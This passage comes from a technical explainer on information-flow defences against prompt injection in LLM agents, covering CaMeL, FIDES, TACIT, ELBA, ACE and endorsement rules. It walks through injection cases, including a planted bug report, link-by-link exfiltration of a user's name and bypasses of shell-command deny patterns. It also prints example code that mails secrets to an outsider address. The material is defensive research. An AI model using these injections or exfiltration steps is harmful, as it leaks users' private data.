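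In Bob's case, the quarantined model extracts the recipient's address from the notes, so the address is labelled untrusted. Under the policy Willison describes, the interpreter sends the document without asking the user only if the user's settings list the address as trusted. Otherwise, it can ask the user to approve the message.

CaMeL also tracks some implicit flows. Garby and colleagues give the example of an injected instruction to email an outsider if a customer's account balance exceeds a threshold. The email contains no figures, but its arrival reveals that the balance is above the threshold. Because the condition reads a secret, CaMeL treats the call inside the branch as secret too and refuses it. The leak Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL arises on the branch the program skips.

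The quarantined model's task is easier than the privileged model's, so it can be smaller, and a user could run it on their own computer. The company that hosts the privileged model would then never see the emails. But someone has to write the policies and keep them up to date. This worries Willison, who still finds such policies hard to think through after two decades in application security. He also expects users who must approve many actions to start approving everything.

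### FIDES

The planner in FIDES chooses one call at a time, as an ordinary agent's does, rather than writing the whole program in advance. It can use trusted results to decide what to do next. Costa and colleagues designed FIDES to hide a result only when showing it would raise the conversation's label.

When a tool returns a value with label ℓ and the conversation has label ℓ_c, FIDES checks whether ℓ ⊑ ℓ_c. If so, it adds the value to the conversation. If not, it stores the value in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name, so ℓ_c stays the same. For lists and records, it applies the test to each part. An email can therefore reach the planner with a readable date and a hidden body.

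The planner has two ways to use hidden text. A tool called `inspect` copies a variable's contents into the conversation, which raises the conversation's label. A tool called `query_llm` sends the contents to a quarantined model with a question and stores the answer in a new variable. The planner can also require an answer in a fixed format, such as yes or no. FIDES enforces the format through constrained decoding, which lets the model produce only tokens that fit.

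The Project X request takes three calls:

| Event | Label of the new value | Label of the conversation afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request arrives | (T, L) | (T, L) |
| The planner searches the mailbox, and FIDES stores the emails as `#read_emails_0` | (U, H) | (T, L) |
| The planner asks `query_llm` to summarise `#read_emails_0`, and FIDES stores the summary as `#query_llm_0` | (U, H) | (T, L) |
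| The planner requests an email to the manager with `#query_llm_0` as the body | call and recipient (T, L), body (U, H) | (T, L) |

FIDES replaces the variable with the summary just before the policy check, so one call can have arguments with different labels. A policy that requires a trusted call and a trusted recipient but accepts an untrusted body lets the email through. The manager must again be on the list of permitted readers.

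If the planner had used `inspect` to read the emails itself, the label would have risen to (U, H), and the monitor would have blocked the email as in the simplest design. A poor choice by the planner therefore makes the agent less useful but not less secure, as long as the policy check is on. Outsiders can still influence the planner when the text is hidden. In the version that Costa and colleagues tested, FIDES hid the subject and body of each email separately, so the planner could still see how many emails there were, and an outsider could change that number by sending more.

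The tested version created variables only for untrusted data. Secret but trusted results went straight into the conversation, so preventing leaks depended on the policies alone.

Garby and colleagues object that CaMeL and FIDES both build the separation of the two models into their architecture. In LLMbda, a programmer can instead create it wherever a program needs it, by forking and clearing the conversation. They also note that CaMeL is more flexible than FIDES because it runs whatever program the model writes, but has no comparable proof. CaMeL's developers call formalisation a "crucial direction" for further work.

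### Tasks that depend on what the agent reads

The Project X request suits these designs because the agent can search, summarise and send whatever the emails contain. Costa and colleagues call such a task data-independent. Let ⟦t⟧(d) be the set of action sequences that solve task t when the agent's data is d, leaving out queries to the model. The task is data-independent if at least one sequence works for all possible data:

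⋂ ⟦t⟧(d) ≠ ∅, taken over every possible d.

Otherwise it is data-dependent. One of their examples is a request to read the latest three emails and create a calendar event if any of them contains a meeting request. The agent has to create an event for some mailboxes and not for others, so no fixed sequence of calls works for every mailbox.

Data-dependent tasks are hard for every design here because of what non-interference demands. Suppose two mailboxes differ only in an outsider's email, which asks for a meeting in one and contains a greeting in the other. Let A be the set of outcomes in which the agent creates an event, and B the set in which it doesn't. If the policy treats the decision to create an event as trusted, the outcomes must have the same probabilities μ in both mailboxes. The agent is then right with probability at most μ(A) in the first and μ(B) in the second, and

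μ(A) + μ(B) ≤ 1.

On average, the agent can be right at most half the time, no better than a coin toss. The same limit applies when unfinished runs are allowed, because the definition used for LLMbda implies it. To do better, the agent would have to let the outsider's email influence a trusted decision, which the rules forbid.

This limit affects each design differently. An agent with a single label for its context cannot create the event after reading the emails. The planner in Wu et al. may read trusted emails, so it can respond to a colleague's request, but it ignores the outsider's. A CaMeL program can branch on the quarantined model's answer, but the calendar call then depends on an untrusted value. The privileged model also has to anticipate every branch when it writes the program.

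In FIDES, the planner can reduce the outsider's influence to a single yes or no:

1. It fetches the emails, which FIDES hides in a variable.
2. It asks the quarantined model whether any of them requests a meeting, and allows only "true" or "false" as an answer.
3. It inspects the answer.
4. If the answer is "true", it asks the quarantined model for the date, time and participants in the format that the calendar tool expects.
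5. It calls the calendar tool with the variable that holds those details.

The answer at step 3 is still untrusted, so a strict policy would block step 5. Costa and colleagues suggest a looser policy that accepts a single bit from an untrusted source, which amounts to endorsement. The outsider could still cause a false event or choose its details.

A fixed set of answers works only if the planner can list the possible actions beforehand. Costa and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to complete the tasks due today in a to-do app. The agent must carry out instructions it reads in the app, and these could require almost any tool. Many of the banking tasks in AgentDojo, the benchmark of simulated office work, tell the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. FIDES blocks most of the resulting actions by design. The user may have good reason to trust the file, but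 unless someone labels it as trusted, the monitor cannot distinguish its instructions from an injection.

Costa and colleagues sorted all 97 of AgentDojo's ordinary tasks by hand:

| Environment | Fixed calls, no model needs to read the data | Fixed calls, a quarantined model reads the data | Calls depend on the data |
|---|---|---|---|
| Workspace | 47.5% | 47.5% | 5.0% |
| Travel | 0% | 90.0% | 10.0% |
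| Banking | 18.7% | 37.5% | 43.8% |
| Slack | 19.0% | 38.1% | 42.9% |

An agent could fix its calls in advance for at least nine in ten tasks in the workspace and travel environments, but for fewer than six in ten in banking and Slack. The benchmark's designers invented these tasks, so the proportions in real offices could be quite different. The quarantined model clearly matters, though, because without it the agent could complete none of the travel tasks with fixed calls.

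### Adoption in products

By late 2026, Microsoft and its subsidiary GitHub had put flow control into several products, mostly as experiments. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced in May that FIDES was available in Agent Framework, the company's toolkit for building agents. Developers have to switch FIDES on. By default, it then hides untrusted results in variables, but a developer can turn off the hiding and rely on a single label for the context. When a call violates the policy, the framework can block it or ask a person to approve it.

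Microsoft illustrates the single-label setting with an agent that sorts bug reports for a public software project. A stranger's report contains a fake system message that tells the agent to read a file of passwords and post the contents as a comment. If the model obeys, the monitor lets it read the file, but the contents are labelled "private", so the context's label rises to private. The comment tool accepts only public data, so the monitor blocks the call to post the comment.

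The announcement also lists limitations. If a developer forgets to label a data source, the framework treats its contents as trusted and public, which is the least safe default. Label creep remains a problem in the single-label setting, where one untrusted report makes the rest of the run untrusted unless the developer removes the report from the context.

Copilot CLI, GitHub's command-line coding agent, has an experimental setting that also keeps one label for the whole context. According to Microsoft, the setting enforces policies only for selected tools on GitHub's own server. That server can label material from public repositories as public and untrusted, and material from private repositories as private and trusted. The policy stops an agent from posting publicly once its context is both untrusted and private. An agent that works only on public repositories, or only on private ones,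 never reaches that combination, so the policy doesn't interrupt it. The labels are coarse, however, because text that an employee copied from outside into a private repository would be labelled trusted.

GitHub Agentic Workflows, which runs agents on repositories automatically, removes untrusted text before the agent sees it. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* describes five levels of integrity: merged, approved, unapproved, none and blocked. "Merged" covers material accepted into the project's main code, and "approved" covers contributions from the project's owners, members and collaborators. The agent receives only items at or above a chosen level. The filtering prevents integrity labels from creeping, but an agent that sorts bug reports may miss those from newcomers. A project maintainer can let a particular report through by marking it as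 approved.

According to GitHub's reference documentation, the filter is on by default for public repositories, with "approved" as the minimum, but private repositories get no automatic policy. The system tracks secrecy labels but does not yet use them to block leaks, so it protects integrity more than confidentiality.

Other companies check tool calls differently. Google Cloud's Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform compares them with the user's intent and plain-language rules, according to UMass Amherst's *Bagdasarian's Contextual Agent Security Adopted in Google Cloud Gemini Enterprise*. Willison reports in *163 posts tagged “prompt-injection”* that Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, uses a classifier by default to approve or block actions.

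Willison also describes a rule in Anthropic's Claude chat application that closely resembles a check on a sink. The tool that opens web pages accepts only addresses that the user typed or that the application's search tool returned. An injection therefore can't make the model add private data to an address and open it.

At first, the tool also accepted links from pages it had already opened. Ayush Paul exploited this with a site that had one link for each letter of the alphabet and instructions for the model to spell out the user's name by following them. The model never had to write an address, but its choice of links revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following such links.

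## Can a type checker reject an unsafe flow before the agent acts?

A monitor such as the one in FIDES checks each tool call when the agent requests it. By the time it refuses a call, the agent may already have made several others, so a task can stop halfway, with a meeting cancelled and no new one booked. If the agent instead writes a whole program before acting, software can examine the program and refuse to run any of it. This doesn't work for an agent that chooses one call at a time, because it chooses each call only after seeing the result of the previous one. *SPA* (2026) notes that agents of this kind typically apply flow control during the run.

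A type checker is the standard software for examining program text. A type describes a value, such as a number or a piece of text, and the checker rejects a program that uses a value where its type does not fit. In some languages, a function's type also describes what the function may do, such as read a file or use the network. Static checks happen before a program runs, and dynamic checks happen while it runs.

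Coding agents already do a crude check before acting by comparing shell commands with lists of forbidden patterns. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes how this can fail. In March 2026, a bug made Claude Code check only the first of several commands joined by "&&". An agent can also start Python and open a forbidden file from there, which a pattern for shell commands will not catch. A type checker avoids both problems because it analyses the whole program in the language the agent writes.

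### Two programs for the Project X mailbox

TACIT, a system from the Swiss university EPFL, has the agent write its actions in the programming language Scala. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) uses "capability" to mean a value that code must hold to affect the outside world, such as a file handle or network connection. (CaMeL's capabilities are tags on data.) Capture checking, an experimental Scala feature, records in each function's type which capabilities the function can use.

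A function that turns text into other text without using any capability is called pure and has the type `String -> String`. It can't send, save or print anything. A function that takes text and sends it through a mail connection called `mail` has the type `String ->{mail} Unit`, where `Unit` means it returns no useful value.

TACIT puts secret text in a container called `Classified`. The agent's code can process the contents only through an operation called `map`, which accepts pure functions and puts the result in a new container. In the invented program below, the mailbox search returns text in such a container, and `summarise` calls a model that has no tools:

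```
val emails = searchMailbox("Project X")
val summary = emails.map(text => summarise(text))
```

The function inside `map` is pure, so the checker accepts the program. Now suppose that the planning model has read an injection in some unclassified file and writes this instead:

```
val emails = searchMailbox("Project X")
emails.map(text => mail.send("outsider@example.com", text))
```

The function inside `map` now has the type `String ->{mail} Unit`. Since `map` requires a function with no capabilities, the compiler rejects the whole program, so not even the mailbox search runs. It would also reject a version that sent the summary to the manager's address, because the rule restricts the use of `mail` regardless of the recipient. To let the agent send the summary, a developer would have to provide a tool that accepts text in its container and checks who may read it.

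Odersky and colleagues trust the compiler, the runtime, TACIT's library and a local model that may read secrets, but they treat the cloud-hosted planning model as a possible attacker. When the agent prints a classified value, the user's terminal shows the real text and the planning model receives only "Classified(\*\*\*\*)". The types keep secrets out of unauthorised files, the network and the planning model's conversation, but they do not cover leaks through timing.

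To test this, the researchers gave agents a software project with a folder of passwords and other secrets. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of ten injections, and added 11 requests in which the user tried to obtain the secrets. With the containers, no secret reached the agent's output in any of the 131 trials for either model. Without them, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in two trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11. Only three of the 13 leaks came from injections, so the test is better evidence of protection against hostile users than against injections.

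On AgentDojo, one of 1,926 injections counted as a success. The agent booked the hotel the user wanted, but its answer quoted a review containing the attacker's recommendation of another hotel.

### Types for effects and trusted values

Zhou and colleagues use Haskell, a language in which the type of a program shows what kinds of effects it can have. Their system, ELBA, works as follows:

1. The application asks the model for a program and specifies its type and the functions it may use.
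2. The model writes the program.
3. The type checker compares the program with the specified type. If they do not match, the model receives the error message and tries again.
4. The application runs the accepted program.

In the main example, an agent compiles bibliographies, and every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. The developer defines an effect type called `BibIO`, with operations to search DBLP, fetch an entry and append an entry to a file. A fetched entry has the type `Trusted Bib`, which the agent's code cannot create in any other way. The agent may fetch several entries, pick the earliest and append it. If its code tries to write an invented entry with Haskell's general `writeFile`, the type checker rejects the program because `writeFile` has the effect type `IO`, not `BibIO`.

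In a test of 100 bibliography tasks, ELBA wrote 925 citations, all with the correct authors, year and identifier. An ordinary agent with a web search tool got at least one of these wrong in 19 of 1,002 citations.

`Trusted` works here as an integrity label that the checker can read. A developer could protect the Project X email in the same way, by defining a type for addresses from the user's request and an email tool that accepts only that type. An address copied from the outsider's email would then have the wrong type.

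A program generated in ELBA can read some data and then call the model again for another program, so the agent can choose its next steps after reading the data. The new program must fit the type required at that point, so it can have fewer permissions than the first program but not more.

Zhou and colleagues prove that these calls to the model do not weaken the type system. Let traces(e) be the set of sequences of externally visible tool calls that a program e can make, and let ⊢ e : t mean that e passes the checker with type t. Suppose that type t guarantees some property P for every ordinary program:

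⊢ e : t implies P(traces(e)).

The theorem extends this guarantee to programs that call the model. The proof replaces each such call with an ordinary function that queries the model, checks the answer and runs it. The result is an ordinary program with the same type and the same traces, so the original guarantee covers it. For the proof to hold, the type system must be sound, but the model can write anything.

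For information flow, however, ELBA uses LIO, an existing Haskell library that checks labels at run time. The types ensure that a program can't bypass these checks. For example, a program might download a web page and then write its text to a place that requires the user's level of trust. The type checker accepts this program, and LIO stops it when it tries to write.

Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA on the Slack tasks in AgentDojo. All four models resisted every standard attack even without policies, so these attacks could not show whether the policies helped. The researchers then simulated the worst case. Whenever data contained an injection, they removed the agent's own task from the prompt and left only the data, so that the model would carry out the attacker's instructions. Each model had 735 runs with policies and 735 without:

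| Model | Injections resisted without policies | Injections resisted with policies | Tasks completed without policies | Tasks completed with policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 57.8% | 100% | 71.2% | 47.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 62.6% | 100% | 75.8% | 42.4% |
| GPT-5.4 | 84.5% | 100% | 75.9% | 46.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 73.5% | 100% | 67.2% | 40.0% |

AgentDojo's scoring counted 29 of the runs with policies as successful attacks. Zhou and colleagues reviewed all 29 and found that the agent had only opened a fixed web address, without leaking anything.

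Turning the policies on reduced the number of completed tasks by between a third and just under half. With the policies on and no attack, ELBA completed eight to ten of the 21 tasks, depending on the model, and CaMeL completed four to six. ELBA took about three times as long because it queried the model more often. The two systems also used different policies, so type checking may not be the reason for ELBA's advantage.

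### Scope as a set of permissions

In most programming languages, code can use only the variables and functions that are in scope, meaning visible at that point in the program. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), from the same EPFL group as TACIT, uses this rule to set an agent's permissions. The system inserts model-written Scala code into the program that requested it. If no email function is in scope there, the generated code can't send email, even if an injection instructs the model to. A developer can therefore allow file access in one step and withhold network access in the next.

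Capture checking prevents code from keeping a permission for later. For example, code may use a file connection inside a block, but the checker rejects the program if the block returns a function that still holds the connection.

Zhao and colleagues also show why it helps to reject a whole program before any of it runs. In their example, the model must subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new balance as a number. It writes code that does the subtraction but returns a sentence. The checker rejects the code, so the balance stays at 100. A language that detected the error only at run time would already have changed the balance.

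The developer decides how narrow the permissions are. If the scope contains a general email function, an injected instruction can make the agent email anyone. In AgentDojo tests, attacks succeeded in seven of 949 trials with Gemini 2.5 Pro and in one of 949 with o4-mini-high. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that their system does not stop an attacker from misusing a capability that the task needs.

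### Checking a plan against a lattice

ACE, short for Abstract-Concrete-Execute, applies Denning's lattice to a plan before it runs. Li, Mallick and colleagues, in *ACE*, presented the system at the NDSS security conference in February 2026. They assume that an attacker may have written one of the apps on the user's device. In an earlier system, IsolateGPT, the planner read the apps' descriptions, and a malicious taxi app could use its description to make the planner ignore a competitor. ACE limits this influence in four steps:

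1. A model reads the user's request without seeing any installed apps. It invents the "abstract apps" it needs, such as one that reads files and one that sends email, and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python.
2. A second model compares the abstract apps with the installed ones, one pair at a time, so an app's description cannot affect the assessment of its competitors.
3. A static analysis follows the labels through the plan. If no choice of apps satisfies the policy, ACE stops with an error.
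4. ACE runs the accepted plan with each app in a separate container, an isolated environment with limited permissions.

ACE treats each app as a sink with its own label, called its clearance, and requires the join of the labels of everything the app receives to be at or below that clearance. The app's output gets the same label as the app, because the app could reveal anything it has clearance to see. For example, the output of an app that loads bank details and has the clearance {financial} is also labelled {financial}. ACE therefore rejects a plan that passes this output to an email app whose only clearance is {personal}.

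Loops need more care. Li and colleagues give this example:

```
a = ""
for i in range(4):
    network_send(a)
    a = load_bank_details()
```

The program sends an empty string on the first iteration of the loop and the bank details on the second. A single pass through the code would miss this, so the analysis repeats its pass over the loop until the labels stop changing. On the second pass, `a` has the label {financial} when it reaches `network_send`, so ACE rejects the plan.

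For an if-statement, the analysis adds the condition's label to every value assigned in either branch. This also catches leaks through skipped assignments, which dynamic labels can miss.

ACE trusts the user's request, the labels and clearances, and its own planning and checking software. The apps' outputs can't add steps to the plan, but they can determine which of its existing branches run. Li and colleagues give no formal guarantee that the analysis catches every leak, because Python is too complex for them to prove it.

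Li and colleagues tested ACE with models that are now old. None of the 1,054 attacks in InjecAgent, a benchmark of indirect injections, made it run an attacker's app. In 2,000 trials on another benchmark, Agent Security Bench, it ran an attacker's app three times, each time because the app's description suited the user's task. These results are expected because the plan already exists when an injection arrives. They are weak evidence about the lattice check, since the benchmarks counted calls to unwanted apps, not leaks between permitted ones.

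In the harmless part of the InjecAgent tasks, ACE used the expected app about 84 per cent of the time with GPT-4o and 61 per cent with Claude 3.7 Sonnet. On a separate tool-use benchmark, GPT-4o reached the correct final result in 80 to 100 per cent of cases, depending on task type.

### What each kind of check misses

A static checker examines every branch of a program before it runs, while a monitor checks only the branch the agent takes. Under a monitor, an agent can therefore pass every check for months until an unusual email leads it into an unsafe branch. A monitor that stops a program because of a secret can also reveal something about the secret, whereas a static rejection reveals nothing about the data if the model wrote the program before reading any of it. However, a static checker may reject a useful program because of a branch that would never have run.

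Static checking is also less precise about labels that become known only during the run. Suppose the manager may read one of the Project X emails, but only the user may read another. The checker runs before either email arrives, so it must give the whole search result one label strict enough for both. A monitor can read each email's label when the email arrives. TACIT similarly waits until the run to check whether a file path is inside the permitted folder, because the program may compute the path while running.

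A static checker can't follow what happens inside an external program that the agent starts. Odersky and colleagues therefore recommend allowing only a short list of safe commands and running them in a sandbox, a restricted environment that limits damage. *Tether* (2026) describes a dynamic check for this case, based on what an action actually does, such as making a network call from inside a Python script. Its policies can carry labels across many steps, and developers can prove facts about the policies, for example that they never allow network access after the agent has read a sensitive file.

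*L3M* (2026) describes a system that uses types to limit generated programs that act on real files, but the system does not yet control information flow. Types can evidently restrict what a program does without restricting where its data goes.

### Can models write code that type-checks?

Capable models can usually write programs that pass the type checker, and error messages help them correct mistakes. In TACIT's tests on τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer service conversations, between 0.3 and 7.9 per cent of the generated programs needed a retry, depending on the model and the type of task. The agents solved 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points more tasks than they did with ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of real software problems, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7 per cent with TACIT and 43.3 per cent without it. ELBA used up its permitted retries in seven of 2,688 runs.

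LACUNA's results are worse. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, it solved 76.0 per cent of 392 tasks on τ²-bench, compared with 90.0 per cent for ordinary tool calls. That is a difference of about 55 tasks, although Zhao and colleagues call the results "on par". With the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, the checker rejected 89 per cent of the programs for telecoms tasks. The researchers suspect that models have seen less Scala than Python in training.

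Far more of ELBA's tasks failed because of its policies than because of type errors, so most of those failures would remain even if the model wrote better Haskell. Zhou and colleagues argue that strict checks can still be useful if an application runs whatever passes and asks a person about the rest. With fewer questions to answer, people might also read them more carefully. According to *L3M*, users approve about 93 per cent of Claude Code's permission requests, which suggests that they often approve out of habit.

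### The model still reads the injection

A type checker constrains what a program does, but it does not prevent untrusted text from influencing the model. Zhao and colleagues say they do not try to prevent this influence, because they consider it unavoidable once the injected text is in the prompt.

In the Project X case, the checker would accept a program that sends the manager a false figure from the outsider's email, since the program has the right type and uses only permitted tools. If the policy also trusts a colleague's address, an injection could cause the model to send the summary there instead, and the checker would accept that program too.

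## When may untrusted text be treated as trusted?

Flow rules can also block an action the user wants. In an example from Garby and colleagues, a user asks an agent to find a friend's payment details on the friend's website and send the friend $50. The account number is untrusted because it comes from the web, and the payment tool accepts only trusted arguments, so the monitor blocks the payment. A better plan would not help, since the agent can find the number only on the website.

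Endorsement makes an exception for such cases. The program explicitly relabels the account number as trusted, so the payment tool accepts it. A reviewer can find that step in the program. FIDES instead has a built-in exception for values from a small set, such as yes or no. Its developers left this exception switched off in their tests. Garby and colleagues object that when such an exception lets a value through, nobody can tell from the run whether it was harmless or a real leak.

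They also tested how much worse an agent performs if it can't endorse anything. Their agent, Randori, attempted 16 banking tasks from AgentDojo three times each, with and without endorsement. With the model Qwen3.7-plus, it succeeded in 36 of 48 runs with endorsement and 30 without. With MiMo-v2.5, it succeeded in 31 with endorsement and 26 without. These differences are well within the margins of error, but three of the tasks require the agent to act on the contents of an untrusted file, which the policy forbids unless the agent can endorse those contents.

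### Who decides what to endorse

Robustness requires that an attacker not decide what a program endorses. In the payment example, the planner can write its program before the agent reads the website. The program fetches the page, extracts one account number, endorses it and sends $50. An attacker who tampers with the page can change the account number, but can't make the program endorse a different amount or a second payment. If the planner reads the page first, the page can influence all of these decisions.

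Randori's planner writes the whole program, including any endorsements (steps that mark untrusted data as trusted), before the agent reads outside data. The agent first tests the program on simulated tools, whose outputs are safe to trust, and uses the real tools only once the program works. It can therefore correct mistakes without showing the planner any untrusted text.

LLMbda, the language in which Randori runs, has a safeguard for agents that read untrusted text before writing code. If a model reads an outsider's email and then writes code that endorses a value, the code runs with an untrusted program-counter label. An endorsed value can't have higher integrity than that label, so it stays untrusted.

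The safeguard fails if an earlier endorsement has relabelled the email as trusted. Code based on the email then runs as trusted, and its own endorsements take effect. To block such chains, Garby and colleagues wrote a function, `robust_endorse`, which adds a mark to the label of every value it endorses. If a value already has the mark, the function stops the program. Values computed from a marked value inherit the mark, so an attacker can't remove it by processing the data further. Developers have to specify which sinks accept marked values.

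Garby and colleagues do not prove that this function makes endorsement robust, partly because robustness is hard to define. Let u₁ and u₂ be two values that an attacker controls, and compare these programs:

- Endorse u₁. If it is true, endorse u₂ and return it. Otherwise, return nothing.
- Select u₂ if u₁ is true and nothing otherwise. Then endorse the selection and return it.

Both programs return the same value with the same label, but in the first, the attacker decides whether the second endorsement happens. A definition that compares only final results, such as non-interference, can't distinguish the two programs.

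Robustness also doesn't restrict the content of an endorsed value. Injections succeeded against Randori in two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill in a text file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with another payment request. Without endorsement, the monitor blocks both this attack and the genuine payment. Garby and colleagues argue that the user's request justifies the endorsement here, because someone who tells an agent to pay the bill in a file has chosen to trust the file.

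### Endorsement and the protection of secrets

LLMbda's `endorse` construct takes a target label and a value. Suppose the target is (i₁, c₁), the value has the label (i₂, c₂), and the program-counter label is (i₀, c₀). The result then has the label

(i₀ ⊔ i₁, c₀ ⊔ c₂).

An endorsed value takes its integrity from the target but keeps its own confidentiality. For example, if a trusted program endorses a password from a private inbox, the password's label changes from (U, H), untrusted and secret, to (T, H), trusted and secret. The password stays secret whatever the target's confidentiality, c₁, is.

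Garby and colleagues prove that endorsement does not weaken the protection of secrets. The theorem concerns an observer at level (U, L), who can see all public data, whether trusted or untrusted. Endorsement can move a value from (U, L) to (T, L), both of which this observer can see, or from (U, H) to (T, H), neither of which the observer can see. Since endorsement never brings a hidden value into view, TIPNI, the form of non-interference that LLMbda satisfies, still holds at this level. The public results do not reveal secrets even if an attacker chooses all the untrusted data, however much a model endorses. A secret may still affect whether a run finishes.

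The same proof covers declassification if we swap the two parts of the label. Releasing a secret then doesn't let untrusted data influence trusted results. But the theorem can't protect the $50, because a payment can go to the wrong account without revealing any secret.

### The small-domain argument

A program can limit an attacker's influence by endorsing only values from a short, fixed list. In an example from Garby and colleagues, an agent replies to an email, using its category as the subject line. The email tool requires a trusted subject, but the category comes from a quarantined model that has read the untrusted email. If the list has n categories, the attacker can choose among at most n outcomes, which is log₂ n bits of information.

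With 8 tags, each call carries at most log₂ 8 = 3 bits, so a hundred calls carry at most 300 bits. A single free-text subject line of 100 printable characters can carry more than 650 bits, which is plenty of room for an injected instruction.

The program has to perform the steps in the right order:

```
tag = ask_quarantined_model(email)
copy = endorse(tag)
if copy is on the fixed list then use copy
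else use tag
```

If the program checked `tag` against the list before endorsing it, the check would depend on untrusted data. This would make the program-counter label untrusted, and the endorsement would have no effect. The program therefore endorses a copy first and uses the copy only if it is on the list. Otherwise, it uses the original, which a strict sink will reject. Garby and colleagues have not yet formally proved the limit of log₂ n bits for their version of this function.

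An attacker who controls only a few bits can still do serious damage. Suppose that one of the eight tags is "invoice approved" and that the program pays the invoice whenever it receives this tag. The attacker then needs to obtain that tag only once. The number of bits limits how many outcomes the attacker can choose between, but not how harmful the worst one is, so a designer also has to check what the program does with each value on the list.

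Small choices can also add up, just as a secret card number can leak one digit at a time. If a program asks for an account number digit by digit and endorses each answer, the attacker can choose the whole number. The program can't list every possible account in advance, so a short list doesn't help with the $50 payment either, unless the user has already saved the friend's account number.

### Type-directed privilege separation

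*Better Privilege Separation for Agents by Restricting Data Types* (Jacob, Alghamdi et al., 2025) loosens the dual-LLM pattern in a similar way. The original pattern rules out an agent that fixes software bugs, for example, because its privileged model would have to learn from a stranger's report which bug to fix. In the looser version, the quarantined model can pass on only integers, decimal numbers, true-or-false values, and choices from a list written by the developer. Free text stays hidden from the privileged model, so an outsider can't send it instructions.

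Passing on one of these values amounts to endorsing it. The developer decides in advance which values to pass on, so an attacker can't influence that decision. But integers and decimal numbers do not form a small domain. An account number is an integer, so an attacker who can't instruct the privileged model might still supply the number it uses in a payment.

Jacob and colleagues built three agents with this method:

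- **Shopping:** The agent looks for a product on a simulated website, where an attacker has added an injection to one of the product's reviews. The quarantined model converts each review into two integers, one for how strongly it supports the product and one for its relevance. The privileged model sees only the number of reviews and the median of each score. If five reviews give support scores of 8, 7, 9, 8 and 0, the median is 8, so one hostile review has little effect. This protection assumes that attackers control only a minority of the reviews.
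- **Scheduling:** The agent arranges meetings by email. The quarantined model reads the correspondence and returns the suggested time slots, which the privileged model compares with the user's calendar. Another model writes the replies but receives only the user's request and the times to propose. A hostile correspondent can still learn which times the user offers, but not what is in the calendar.
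- **Bug fixing:** The quarantined model reads the bug report and returns the position of a file in a list, along with line numbers. The privileged model has to repair the bug without reading the report.

| Agent | Model | Tasks completed without the defence | Tasks completed with it | Attacks successful without it | Attacks successful with it |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping | GPT-4o | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
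| Scheduling | GPT-4o | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | Claude Sonnet 4 | 49.7% | 14.6% | 94.3% | 0% |

Each agent faced only one fixed injection text, so the zeros alone are weak evidence. The stronger reason to expect them is that the privileged model never receives the injection. The defence did not measurably reduce the first two agents' performance, but the bug-fixing agent lost about 70 per cent of its successes. Jacob and colleagues attribute this to the missing description of the bug, since a line number only gives the bug's location.

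An outsider can also lie without giving any instructions. For example, a flood of negative posts could mislead an agent that trades shares according to social media, even if the privileged model saw only numbers.

### Labels based on influence

Endorsement changes the label of data that untrusted text may have influenced. An application can instead try to find out which text influenced the model's output, and ignore the labels of the rest. *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues, 2024) gives the example of a user who asks for the population of New York City. A search returns similar figures from a trusted source and an untrusted one. The usual join rule labels the answer untrusted, although the model could have answered from the trusted source alone.

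Their method looks for a lower label that would be enough. Let x be the user's request, C the set of retrieved documents, and y the model's answer. For a lower label L′, let C′ be the documents whose labels are at or below L′. The label L′ qualifies if

U(y | x, C) − U(y | x, C′) ≤ λ.

U is the negative of perplexity, a standard measure of how surprising a text is to a model. A small difference means that the model would have been almost as likely to write y without the excluded documents. The developer sets the tolerance λ. The whole procedure has four steps:

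1. The model answers from all the documents.
2. Software searches for the lowest labels that qualify, and the application picks one.
3. The model answers again, using only the documents at or below that label.
4. The application discards the first answer and returns the second with the lower label.

The third step makes the method safe because the new answer can't contain anything from a document that the model didn't receive, even if an attacker distorts the measurement in the second step. A bad measurement can therefore reduce the answer's quality but not its security. The excluded documents still have an indirect influence, because they help determine which label qualifies. An outsider might be able to use this influence to prevent a trusted answer from appearing, much as a secret can affect whether a program finishes.

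Siddiqui and colleagues tested the search on Llama 2 models, which are now very old. On 64 artificial questions with 14 documents each, it found exactly the right labels 86 per cent of the time. Asking the model which documents it had used worked at most 13 per cent of the time. On questions about news articles, the search lowered the label in 39 to 57 per cent of the cases where this was possible, provided that the relevant articles had been retrieved. In a test based on 40 handwritten agent conversations, they report that the search gave a more permissive label than asking the model did in over 85 per cent of cases.

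The method reduces label creep when a task doesn't need the untrusted text. It can't help with the $50 payment, because without the website the model has no account number to return.

### Can measured influence carry a guarantee?

In November 2026, Xu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Sightline*, presented a faster way to measure influence. Their tool uses attention, the mechanism by which most LLMs move information between tokens. A model has many attention heads. As it produces each output token, every head distributes a total weight of 1 over the tokens so far. For a passage S and an output position t, Sightline adds up the weights that a head gives to the passage:

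m(S) = Σ aₜᵢ, taken over every token i in S.

A simple classifier combines these sums from all the heads into a score for the passage. If the score falls below a threshold, the application drops the passage's label. The measurement takes 0.12 to 0.20 seconds per call. If a company doesn't expose its model's attention weights, an open model can process the same prompt and output instead, with about the same accuracy.

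Xu and colleagues prove that a small change to a passage can affect the output only through attention to that passage. They also prove that an application can't safely ignore a passage just because it receives very little attention. In their counterexample, an attention head gives a passage a weight of about two billionths. If the passage had said something else, the head would have given it almost all its attention, and the output would have been different. This is an implicit flow, like the one through a branch that a program doesn't take.

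Sightline therefore offers a statistical guarantee. The researchers collect passages that are known to have influenced an output, one from each of n groups of software projects. To miss at most a share α of such passages, they calculate

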